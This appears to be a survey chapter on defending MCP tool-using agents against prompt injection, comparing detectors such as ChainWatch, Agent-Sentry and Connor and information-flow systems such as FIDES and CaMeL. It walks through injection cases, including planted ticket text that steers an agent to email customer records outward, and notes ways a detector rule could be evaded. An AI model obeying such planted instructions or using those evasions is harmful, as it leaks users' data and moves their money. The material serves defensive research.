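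### The lethal trifecta and toxic flows

The best-known rule for dangerous combinations comes from the programmer Simon Willison. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, lists three capabilities that together let an attacker steal data:

- access to private data
- exposure to content that an attacker could have written
- a way to send data out

The support-ticket agent has all three, through the customer database, the tickets and the mail server. Willison advises against having all three at once when combining tools from different sources.

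The rule applies to a set of tools, so an operator can use it before the agent runs. In a log, the operator can make the rule stricter by also checking the order of calls. The outward call has to come after the agent has read both the planted text and the data, because the text cannot influence calls made before it was read and the agent cannot send data it has not yet read.

The trifecta covers only data theft. A planted invoice can make an agent pay a stranger without leaking any private data, so an operator would need another rule for payments and deletions.

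Toxic-flow analysis, which Invariant Labs (2025) previewed that July, searches for such combinations automatically. It builds a graph of the sequences in which an agent could call its tools, and labels each tool by how trustworthy its content is, how sensitive its data is and whether it could send data out. It then scores the paths that could lead to a violation, such as the one in the GitHub case. The analysis can also use records from running agents. *Agent Scan*, from Snyk, the security company that owns Invariant Labs, checks the tools installed on a machine for toxic flows.

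### How many set-ups meet the rule

In *Parasites in the Toolchain*, Zhao, Hou and colleagues (2025) examined 12,230 tools on 1,360 public MCP servers. They found 128 servers with a tool that brings in outside text, 155 with one that reads private data and 96 with one that can send data out. Only two servers had all three kinds of tool.

Combinations of servers meet the rule much more often. If people chose from this collection at random, about 4% of sets of five servers and 21% of sets of ten would have all three capabilities. But people choose servers that are useful to them, and many want web pages, files and email. Zhao and colleagues describe a web fetcher, a file server and Gmail as a typical office set-up, which meets the rule.

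The counts are probably too low. A first review marked 5,666 tools as potentially risky, but the study counted only the 1,062 that showed a risky capability when tested. About 30% of the servers also needed outside accounts that were hard to get.

The labels are also partly a matter of judgement. The study counted only three of 54 communication and email servers as bringing in outside text, but Willison treats any tool that reads email as a source of untrusted content. By that standard, an email server that can read and send messages meets the rule by itself.

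Pynt, a security company, rated 52% of set-ups with three MCP servers as high risk. Its rule is broad, because a server needs only to accept untrusted input and have a sensitive capability to meet it. According to *MCP Poses Security Risks*, the researcher did not disclose how he estimated the risk for several servers, so the figure is hard to interpret.

An attack can fail even when a set-up meets the rule. Zhao and colleagues built ten chains of three tools and attacked each one ten times in Cursor. Nine chains leaked data at least once, and 36 of the 100 attempts succeeded. In a separate test of the office set-up, GPT-5 and Claude 4.5 Sonnet each resisted all 75 attempts, while DeepSeek-R1 and Gemini 2.5 Flash each leaked data in more than 70% of theirs. The trifecta would flag the set-up with any of these models, so it is more useful for deciding which tools to connect than for raising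 an alarm during a session.

### ChainWatch and the stages of an attack

*ChainWatch* is a design for a proxy that would follow the whole session and estimate how far an attack had progressed. The proxy would turn each call into 20 numbers, or features:

- **Type of tool (5):** whether the call reads, writes, runs a program, uses the network or changes a configuration
- **Sensitivity (1):** a score for the arguments, which is higher for passwords than for file paths
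- **Data flow (4):** whether the call reads internal data, writes to an outside destination, carries data from an earlier call or crosses to another server
- **Timing (3):** the gap since the last call, the rate of calls and the age of the session
- **Output (7):** warning signs in what the server returns, such as instructions, encoded data or a changed tool definition

A hidden Markov model then assigns each call to one of six stages: reconnaissance, trust building, injection, escalation, lateral movement and exfiltration. The stages are hidden because no log records them, so the model has to infer them from the features. It uses three sets of probabilities: π for the stage at the start, *A* for moving from one stage to the next, and *B* for the features a call is likely to have at each stage. The joint probability of stages *s*₁, *s*₂, … and features *v*₁, *v*₂, … is

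π(*s*₁) · *B*(*v*₁ | *s*₁) · *A*(*s*₂ | *s*₁) · *B*(*v*₂ | *s*₂) · …

The usual method is to choose the sequence of stages that makes this product largest. A call's label therefore depends on the calls around it. For example, reading a file may look like escalation if an earlier result contained instructions, but like reconnaissance at the start of a session.

Five rules then look for suspicious patterns in the last ten calls.

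| Rule | What triggers it | Response |
|---|---|---|
| R1 | Reconnaissance followed directly by access to sensitive data | Warning |
| R2 | Access to two or more servers, with signs of sensitive data flow | Warning |
| R3 | A read at a late stage, then a network call carrying the data within five steps | Block |
| R4 | A jump of two or more stages | Warning |
| R5 | A configuration change at the escalation stage or later | Block |

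In one of the paper's five scenarios, an attacker uses a banking agent to move money to a new account:

1. `get_balance` checks the balance, which counts as reconnaissance.
2. `list_payees` lists the existing payees, which counts as trust building.
3. `add_payee` adds the attacker's account. This counts as escalation, two stages further on, so R4 raises a warning.
4. `transfer_funds` sends the money. This counts as exfiltration, and according to the paper, R3 blocks it.

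R3's wording does not quite fit this case because it requires a read at a late stage, and the only late call before the transfer is a write. The design might therefore produce only warnings. More seriously, a user's request to pay a new landlord could produce the same four calls.

ChainWatch is a design specification that its researchers have not tested empirically. They assigned the feature values in the scenarios by hand, and the model's transition probabilities still have to be estimated from real sessions. They found no benchmark with labelled sessions in which harmless-looking calls build up to an attack. *MCPHunt*'s public collection of 6,786 recorded runs could at least help measure false alarms.

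The model would probably raise many false alarms, because none of its six stages represents ordinary work. Trust building comes closest, but one of its listed signs is the absence of cross-server calls. Their presence is a sign of lateral movement, so the model could mistake an ordinary hop for part of an attack. The researchers acknowledge that R2 could also give false alarms in company workflows that span several services. An attacker who knew the limits could evade R3 by having the agent make six harmless calls between reading the data and sending it.

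### Agent-Sentry and learning from past runs

A detector can also learn what an agent's legitimate runs look like. *Agent-Sentry* (Sequeira, Damianakis and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that learns where the arguments of legitimate calls come from. This system is separate from AgentSentry, described earlier, which reruns an agent from a snapshot.

Agent-Sentry requires the agent to report the source of each argument and whether it copied, derived or generated the value. These reports form a provenance graph, which links each call to the user's request and to the earlier calls that supplied its values. An operator also has to mark which tools return untrusted content and which have outside effects. Agent-Sentry then checks each call with an outside effect in up to three steps:

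1. **Classifier:** A model made of 100 small decision trees estimates the probability that the call is malicious. Its 17 features cover the order of calls, the sources of the arguments and whether a value appears in untrusted text. It allows calls below 0.33, blocks those at 0.66 or above and passes the rest on.
2. **List of known values:** Agent-Sentry allows the call if its recipients, accounts and similar values are familiar from earlier legitimate runs and come from trusted sources.
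3. **Judge:** A language model compares any remaining call with the user's request and excerpts from the untrusted content.

In one of the paper's examples, some users ask the agent to email someone called Lily. In an attack, the user only wants to delete a calendar event, but planted text contains an instruction to email Lily. A list of permitted recipients would have to allow both emails or block both. Agent-Sentry detects that the address came from a tool result, and the judge then finds no request to email anyone.

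Planted text can trigger a call without supplying any of its arguments. In the SSH-key attack described earlier, it made the agent clear its memory with a call that had no arguments. Sequeira and colleagues' claim that an injected action always takes at least one argument from untrusted content is therefore too strong.

To train and test the system, the researchers collected 5,380 runs from seven agents, including 2,081 in which an attack succeeded. A language model wrote 757 user tasks, and the researchers added 3,734 rewordings of them. They also tested the system on the original tasks from AgentDojo and AgentDyn.

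| Version and test | Harmless runs allowed | Attacks blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Full system, new dataset | 96.4% | 96.8% |
| Judge alone with a tuned prompt, new dataset | 98.0% | 95.4% |
| Judge alone with an untuned prompt, new dataset | 82.0% | 75.5% |
| Full system, original tasks not used in training | 64.4% | 90.9% |
| Version with simple rules in place of the classifier, same original tasks | 79.1% | 95.0% |

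On the new dataset, the system wrongly blocked 3.6% of harmless runs. At the attack rate of one in 1,000 assumed earlier, it would raise about 37 false alarms for each attack it blocked. With a tuned prompt, the judge alone did about as well as the full system, so the classifier's main benefits are speed and less dependence on the judge's prompt. The full system sent 3.1% of decisions to the judge and added about 0.07 seconds per run, compared with 2.4 seconds for the judge alone.

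The system did much worse on unfamiliar tasks, where it blocked more than a third of harmless runs, and more than half for the shopping agent. In the training data, users mostly stated at least one sensitive detail, such as an account number. In the original tasks, these details are often only in a document, as when the user asks the agent to "pay the bill" in a named file. To the classifier, a legitimate account number from that file looks much like one an attacker planted. Many data-carrying hops work this way, so a system trained on one group of users could block a lot of useful work for another.

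The paper's abstract gives better figures for AgentDojo and AgentDyn, with 95.1% of harmless runs allowed and 94.3% of attacks blocked. These figures come from the version with simple rules, which the researchers fitted and tested on the same runs. When they held back a fifth of the runs for testing, it allowed 87.1% of harmless runs and blocked 93.2% of attacks.

Agent-Sentry also relies on the agent to report its sources accurately, even though planted text may already be steering the agent. The system checks some reports against the recorded text, which reduces this risk but does not remove it. The judge may also miss a fake invoice that looks just like a real one, because the attacker's account number appears where a legitimate one would.

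### Connor and servers that break their promises

Huang, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *From Component Manipulation to System Compromise*, look for malicious servers. Their system, Connor, compares what a server does with the stated function of its tools:

1. It checks the command that starts the server for malicious instructions.
2. It uses a language model to separate each tool's stated function from any instructions planted in its description.
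3. It writes requests that should lead an agent to use the tool, then runs them in a simulated host.
4. After each step, a judging model compares the tool's behaviour and code with its stated function, taking earlier steps into account.

The history lets Connor connect a tool that reads a password with a later step that sends it out.

In a test with 134 malicious and 130 harmless servers, Connor detected 91.1% of the malicious ones (recall), and 98.4% of its alerts were correct (precision). Its F1 score, the harmonic mean of the two, was 94.6%. The researchers built 114 of the malicious servers themselves. Connor missed nine of the 20 built by others, though eight of those nine had goals it was not designed to detect, such as returning false information.

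Connor flagged nine of 1,672 servers from public marketplaces, and two of those nine were malicious. One gave an attacker remote control of the user's computer. The other was presented as a to-do list manager, but its results contained instructions for the agent to call a second tool, which searched for cryptocurrency wallet files and sent them away. Nobody checked all the other servers by hand, so the number of malicious servers Connor missed is unknown.

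MCP-scan, which includes toxic-flow analysis, flagged 212 of the same servers, but none were confirmed as malicious. In the labelled test, some of its false alarms involved combinations of tools that could have leaked data but did not. These results partly reflect a difference in purpose, because toxic-flow analysis warns about what benign tools could do together.

Connor found only 28.4% of the malicious servers when it did not analyse their code. An execution log does not contain that code, so a detector that relies on the log would probably miss many of the same attacks.

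Connor checks whether a server does what its tool descriptions promise, not whether the user asked for a call. In the support-ticket log, the mail server sends an email as its tool description promises, so Connor would have no reason to flag it, even though the user never asked for the email. Conversely, the postmark-mcp package leaked messages even when the agent made only the calls the user wanted. The researchers left attacks between servers for future work.

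### What each method needs and misses

| Method | What it needs | What it can miss |
|---|---|---|
| Trifecta and toxic-flow analysis | Accurate labels for every tool | Unwanted payments and deletions, and outward channels that nobody has labelled |
| ChainWatch | All calls and results in one place, and labelled sessions for training | Attacks that resemble ordinary work or unfold slowly |
| Agent-Sentry | Many recorded runs of similar tasks, the user's request and reliable reports of where values came from | Attacks that imitate legitimate runs |
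| Connor | A server it can run, with readable code and a clear statement of what each tool does | Planted text that passes through an honest server, and malicious code that never runs during the test |

The type of evidence a detector uses matters more than whether it learns from data. In Shavit's test, detectors trained on users' habits did much worse than a request check at catching sessions hijacked by planted text. Agent-Sentry also learns from past behaviour, but it tracks the source of each argument and can consult the request. If a user asked the agent to email Dana Reyes's contact record to a courier, the calls to the customer database and the mail server could look the same as in the attack. Only the request and the source of the recipient's address would distinguish the two cases.

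## Blocking a hop when it happens

A detector that scores sequences of calls will sometimes misclassify them. Another approach, called information-flow control, is to label the data an agent reads and use ordinary code to block any call that breaks a fixed rule about those labels. Computer scientists have studied this method since the 1970s. It can stop a hop even after planted text has steered the model into attempting it.

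### How the labels work

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, use labels with two parts. One part records whether the data is trusted, and the other lists who may read it. Their method has three steps:

1. **Label each result.** The text of a support ticket is untrusted, because a stranger could have written it, and only the support team may read it. The user's own request normally counts as trusted and public.
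2. **Combine the labels.** Anything made from two pieces of data is trusted only if both pieces are, and only people who may read both pieces may read it.
3. **Check the call.** Before a call runs, code compares its label with the rule for that tool.

If *t* is the trust part and *R* is the set of permitted readers, the second step is

(*t*₁, *R*₁) ⊔ (*t*₂, *R*₂) = (*t*₁ ⊔ *t*₂, *R*₁ ∩ *R*₂)

where ⊔ means "combined with". A model's output can draw on anything in its context, so it gets the combined label of the whole context. One untrusted email therefore makes every later decision untrusted.

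*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) describes two rules as enough for most tools. A call that changes something may go ahead only if the agent decided on it in a trusted context. A call that sends data may also go ahead if every recipient has permission to read that data.

Suppose an agent has a ticket server and a mail server. The user asks it to email a summary of ticket 41 to Priya on the support team and then close the ticket. The ticket contains a planted instruction to send a copy to an outside address.

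| Step | Context after the step | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| The user makes the request | Trusted, public | None needed |
| `tickets.read` returns ticket 41 | Untrusted, support team only | Allowed, because reading changes nothing |
| `mail.send` to Priya | Unchanged | Allowed, because Priya may read the ticket |
| `mail.send` to records@outside.example | Unchanged | Refused, because the context is untrusted and the recipient may not read the ticket |
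| `tickets.close` | Unchanged | Refused, because the context is untrusted |

The rules prevent the leak without anyone having to recognise the planted text as an instruction. However, they also stop the agent from closing the ticket, which the user wanted it to do. The planted text could still change what the email to Priya says, because the rule about readers limits only where data goes.

### FIDES, CaMeL and SAMOS

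| | FIDES | CaMeL | SAMOS |
|---|---|---|---|
| What has a label | Each piece of data | Each value in a program | Each tool |
| What the label records | Trust and permitted readers | Source and permitted readers | High or low confidentiality |
| Where the check runs | The agent's planning loop | The interpreter that runs the program | A gateway |
| What happens to untrusted text | The planning model sees it only if it asks to | The planning model never sees it | The model reads it as usual |

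**FIDES**, Costa and colleagues' system, avoids the refusal to close the ticket by hiding untrusted text from the model that plans the calls. It stores the ticket in a variable and shows the planning model only the variable's name. The planning model can pass the variable to a quarantined model, which has no tools, and email the resulting summary without reading it. The planning model's context stays trusted, so the agent can also close the ticket.

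If the next step depends on the text, the planning model can get a yes-or-no answer from the quarantined model. A policy can accept that answer because one bit leaves almost no room for a planted instruction. The planning model can also read the whole text, but its context then becomes untrusted.

In tests on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, Costa and colleagues counted 152 successful attacks on an undefended agent and none on one using FIDES. AgentDojo's scoring recorded three successes against FIDES, but the researchers checked them by hand and rejected them. They had marked a type of data as untrusted whenever an AgentDojo attack used it. The result therefore shows that the rules work when the labels are right, but not that an operator would choose the right labels. Across four areas of work, agents with FIDES completed 41% to 59% of harmless tasks, compared with 70% to 98.8% without a defence.

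**CaMeL**, which Google DeepMind introduced in 2025, separates planning from untrusted data more strictly. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) explains that a privileged model reads only the user's request and writes the whole plan as a program in restricted Python. An interpreter runs the program and calls the tools. When the plan needs a detail from untrusted text, such as an email address, a quarantined model extracts it and the interpreter records its source. Planted text can change that value but cannot add a step to the plan. A policy can then block a message if the recipient's address came from an untrusted source.

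*AutoDojo* (2026) retested CaMeL on five models, including Claude Haiku 4.5 and GPT-5.4-mini. In its tests, attacks succeeded at most 6.4% of the time on any model with CaMeL, and agents completed no more than two thirds of harmless tasks. Without a defence, fixed attacks on one of the models, Gemini 2.5 Flash, succeeded 50.4% of the time.

CaMeL is also slow. *AttriGuard* (2026) measured an average of 165 seconds per task with Gemini 2.5 Flash, compared with 11 seconds without a defence. With Llama 3.3 70B, the averages were 105 and 14 seconds. *ToolFence* (2026) attributes the delay to writing and interpreting a program, rewriting it after errors, and calling the quarantined model. In an earlier test with GPT-4o, *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) found that the median task needed 2.8 times as many input tokens and 2.7 times as many output tokens.

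FIDES can cost much more than CaMeL. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) reports that 17 computer-use tasks cost a total of $76.07 with FIDES and $5.40 with CaMeL. Costa and colleagues had not tried to make FIDES efficient.

CaMeL's planning model has to write code that handles a tool's result before it has seen one. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), which extends CaMeL to several agents, found that agents completed a reasonable share of tasks only after the researchers added full return formats to the tool descriptions. The paper describes this as a modest, one-time job. It would be a bigger job for someone who connects many outside MCP servers, whose tools can change.

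CaMeLoT, by Nikolaou and colleagues, checks CaMeL's plan against rules before any tool runs. For example, it can reject a plan that would disconnect a computer from the network without first getting approval. It returns the sequence of steps that breaks the rule, which the model can use to repair the plan. An operator could use the same method to reject an unwanted hop before the agent makes its first call. CaMeLoT treats loops cautiously, so it may also reject some safe plans.

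**SAMOS** is much simpler. *Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows* (Ntousakis, 2026), a master's thesis at Brown University, describes it as a gateway that tracks the confidentiality of a whole session. A developer or administrator labels each tool with the confidentiality, high or low, of the sources it reads from and writes to. The host only needs its settings changed to send all calls through the gateway.

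Ntousakis applies SAMOS to the GitHub attack described earlier. Reading a public issue gives the session a low level, so the gateway blocks the agent's later attempt to read a private repository. A fixed label for each tool isn't enough, because the same tool reads both public and private files. Either the tool has to report the confidentiality of each file, or the developer has to split the tool in two.

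The thesis reports no measurements of security, task completion or overhead beyond this one case. The rule could also stop the agent from comparing a public bug report with private code when the user wants it to. SAMOS has no label for trust, so it might let a planted email trigger a payment if the mailbox and the bank account are both labelled highly confidential.

### The objection that labels stop useful work

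According to Kolluri and colleagues, strict rules of this kind have lowered task completion on AgentDojo by up to 30%. The loss is greatest on tasks where the agent has to read something before it knows what to do. Such tasks make up more than 40% of AgentDojo's banking and Slack tasks, but no more than 10% of those in its other two areas. Many banking tasks require the agent to follow instructions in a file, and FIDES blocks most of the resulting actions. CaMeL has the same difficulty, as it showed by failing every AgentDyn task with GPT-4o.

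Blocking may cause fewer task failures with better models. FIDES completed 41% of AgentDojo's travel tasks with GPT-4o and 68% with o1, a reasoning model that was better at working with variables.

Kolluri and colleagues also argue that the usual comparison is unfair because it sets a defended agent that cannot ask for permission against an undefended agent that never needs it. In practice, agents such as GitHub Copilot ask the user before most calls that change something, and labels can show which of these questions are unnecessary. The researchers therefore counted the AgentDojo tasks that an agent could complete without asking anyone. The table gives their results with o3-mini.

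| Agent | Tasks completed without asking the user |
|---|---|
| Asks before every call with consequences | 24.3% |
| Asks only when a call breaks a label rule | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 50.1% |
| PRUDENTIA | 59.1% |

PRUDENTIA, the successor to FIDES, gives the planning model the labels and rules so that it can look for a plan that follows them. Before reading hidden text, the model must explain why it needs to and list the calls it expects to make afterwards.

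PRUDENTIA can also ask the user to endorse a piece of data, which makes that data trusted. If an email lists ten jobs for the agent, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten calls. With o4-mini, PRUDENTIA needed 19.2 approvals on average across all the tasks it completed, compared with 36.8 for FIDES. Their completion rates were similar, at 73.2% for PRUDENTIA and 75.7% for FIDES.

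This is a good reply for agents that would otherwise ask about every change. It does little for people who have chosen "Always Allow", because the labels add interruptions for them. The researchers also assumed that users would approve every legitimate call and stop every attack. Endorsement makes a mistake more harmful, because a user who overlooks one planted line in the email has approved whatever that line leads to.

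FIDES, CaMeL and PRUDENTIA all trust tool descriptions. The WhatsApp attack through the fact tool's description is therefore outside what they promise to stop.

### Keeping secrets out of later calls

Adding instructions to a prompt is easier than installing a label system. *MCPHunt*, the benchmark of secrets moving between servers without an attacker, tested three levels of instruction. The first was a brief reminder about privacy, the second listed the kinds of secret to remove, and the third explained the risk of moving data between systems and gave examples of safe output.

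With GPT-5.4, the most detailed instructions reduced unnecessary copying of secrets from 13.9% of runs to 0.3%, while task completion stayed about the same (79.4% before, 80.5% after). The brief reminder reduced copying only to 8.1%.

The instructions worked less well for the other two models. The table shows all copying in one of the benchmark's environments, including copying that the task required.

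| Model | No instructions | Brief reminder | Detailed instructions |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4 | 24.3% | 19.6% | 1.9% |
| DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 47.2% | 47.2% | 12.0% |
| MiniMax-M2.7 | 50.9% | 48.1% | 26.9% |

These rates depend on the model following the instructions, and the environment contained no text telling it to do otherwise, which an attacker could add.

*MCPHunt* also tested a guard that does not rely on the model. It marks secrets when the agent reads them, then redacts them when the agent tries to write them somewhere else. The paper compared DeepSeek-V4-Flash with and without the guard on tasks that move web content into local storage, the pathway with the most copying. In 39 pairs of runs, the guard reduced the share of runs with an unsafe write from 79.5% to 51.3%. Task completion was 76.9% without the guard and 79.5% with it, a difference that could be due to chance.

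The researchers do not say why about half of the guarded runs were still unsafe, but an earlier run with the same model suggests a reason. In that run, all the remaining leaks were on the web pathway. Some secrets had arrived through the server that fetches web pages, and the guard did not redact them later because it had not marked that server's results. The same gap probably explains at least part of the 51.3%. A label system would fail in the same way if an operator forgot to label one of the servers that can return a secret.

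The first version of the paper claimed much stronger results for the guard, including no unsafe writes for four of five models. The researchers have withdrawn those claims because they could not find anything that reproduced them.

### Helping the agent finish the task

If a guard only refuses a call, the agent may give up on the user's task or try the same thing another way. *HARDE* (Liu, Li and colleagues, 2026) therefore describes a system that also tells the agent how to continue. The system uses no data labels. A filter allows routine calls, blocks obviously dangerous ones and passes the rest to a monitoring model, which compares each call with the user's request and the earlier steps.

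In one of their tests, a user asks an agent to upload new files to GitHub. One of the files contains an instruction to invite trustme@gmail.com to a repository. When the agent tries to send the invitation, the monitor gives the call a suspicion score of 95 out of 100, above the limit of 75, and blocks it. The monitor records that the invitation came from a file, not the user, then sends the agent an instruction to drop the invitation and continue the upload. The agent then replaces the altered file with the clean version from GitHub and finishes the task.

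HARDE also adjusts itself, using a coding agent that studies test runs and rewrites the filter, the monitor's instructions or the feedback, one at a time. With DeepSeek-V4-Flash as both agent and monitor, the share of AgentDyn cases in which the attack failed and the user's task succeeded rose from 81.6% without a defence to 93.5%.

The adjustment mattered most with a weaker monitor. Before the adjustment, the small model Qwen3-8B stopped every attack but blocked so much else that only 13.6% of cases ended well. Afterwards, it still stopped every attack, and 94.7% of cases ended well. On SHADE-Arena, a harder benchmark, removing the feedback lowered that share from 50.0% to 15.4%. This evidence is weak because SHADE-Arena has only 17 cases and hides the attacker's goal in the system prompt rather than in a tool result.

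HARDE preserves much more useful work than the label systems did in their tests, including on tasks where the agent has to adapt. But it gives no guarantee, because the monitor also reads the planted text and an attacker could try to mislead it. The existing attacks that Liu and colleagues used were not written to do this. They also adjusted the system on 36 cases from AgentDyn before testing it on others from the same benchmark. An operator could use fixed rules for the most harmful calls and a monitor for the rest.

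### Blocking, asking or alerting afterwards

The best response to a suspicious hop depends on how likely it is to be unwanted and what each mistake would cost. Suppose that blocking always works and that users always approve the calls they want. The expected costs are then:

- **Block:** (1 − *p*)*B*
- **Ask first:** *A* + *peH*
- **Alert afterwards:** *r* + *pH*′

Here *p* is the probability that the hop is unwanted, *B* is the loss from stopping a wanted hop, and *A* is the loss from interrupting the user. *H* is the harm from an unwanted hop, and *e* is the chance that the user approves an unwanted hop by mistake. *H*′ is the harm that remains after someone reads the alert and undoes what they can, and *r* is the loss from having someone read it.

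The table uses invented values to show how the answer changes. It sets *B* at $20, *A* at $1, *r* at $0.10 and *e* at 10%.

| Hop | *p* | *H* | *H*′ | Block | Ask | Alert |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Emailing customer records to an address found only in a ticket | 50% | $10,000 | $10,000 | **$10.00** | $501.00 | $5,000.10 |
| Paying an invoice that the user asked the agent to pay | 1% | $1,000 | $1,000 | $19.80 | **$2.00** | $10.10 |
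| Copying a date from an email into the user's calendar | 1% | $10 | $2 | $19.80 | $1.01 | **$0.12** |

Blocking suits hops that are probably unwanted and hard to undo, such as sending confidential data to a recipient the user never mentioned, giving a stranger access to an account, or running code from an untrusted page. For the customer records in the table, asking users for approval would be better than blocking only if they wrongly approved fewer than about one in 550 such requests.

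Asking the user is better when they may well want the call but their request doesn't specify an important detail. For example, the account number for an invoice payment may appear only in the invoice, or the user may have told the agent to follow the instructions in a ticket, and those include messaging someone outside the company.

Kolluri and colleagues warn that people asked to confirm too often begin to approve requests without reading them (confirmation fatigue), so each unnecessary question raises *e* for the important ones. In PRUDENTIA, code decides when to ask, so planted text cannot suppress the question. The text could still affect what the user sees, as the misleading WhatsApp dialog showed. A request to approve a payment should therefore show the full account number and identify the document it came from.

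Alerts work for hops that someone can reverse, such as a calendar entry or a copy of a file inside the user's own systems. They can also work for a password an agent has copied into a local database, if someone deletes the copy or changes the password before an outsider can read it. Once a secret has left the organisation, an alert can only help limit further damage.

In the support-ticket log, the agent's lookup of Dana Reyes in the customer database would justify at most an alert, because the record stayed inside the company. The gateway should block the email that followed, tell the agent not to retry it, and still let the agent post the summary the user asked for.
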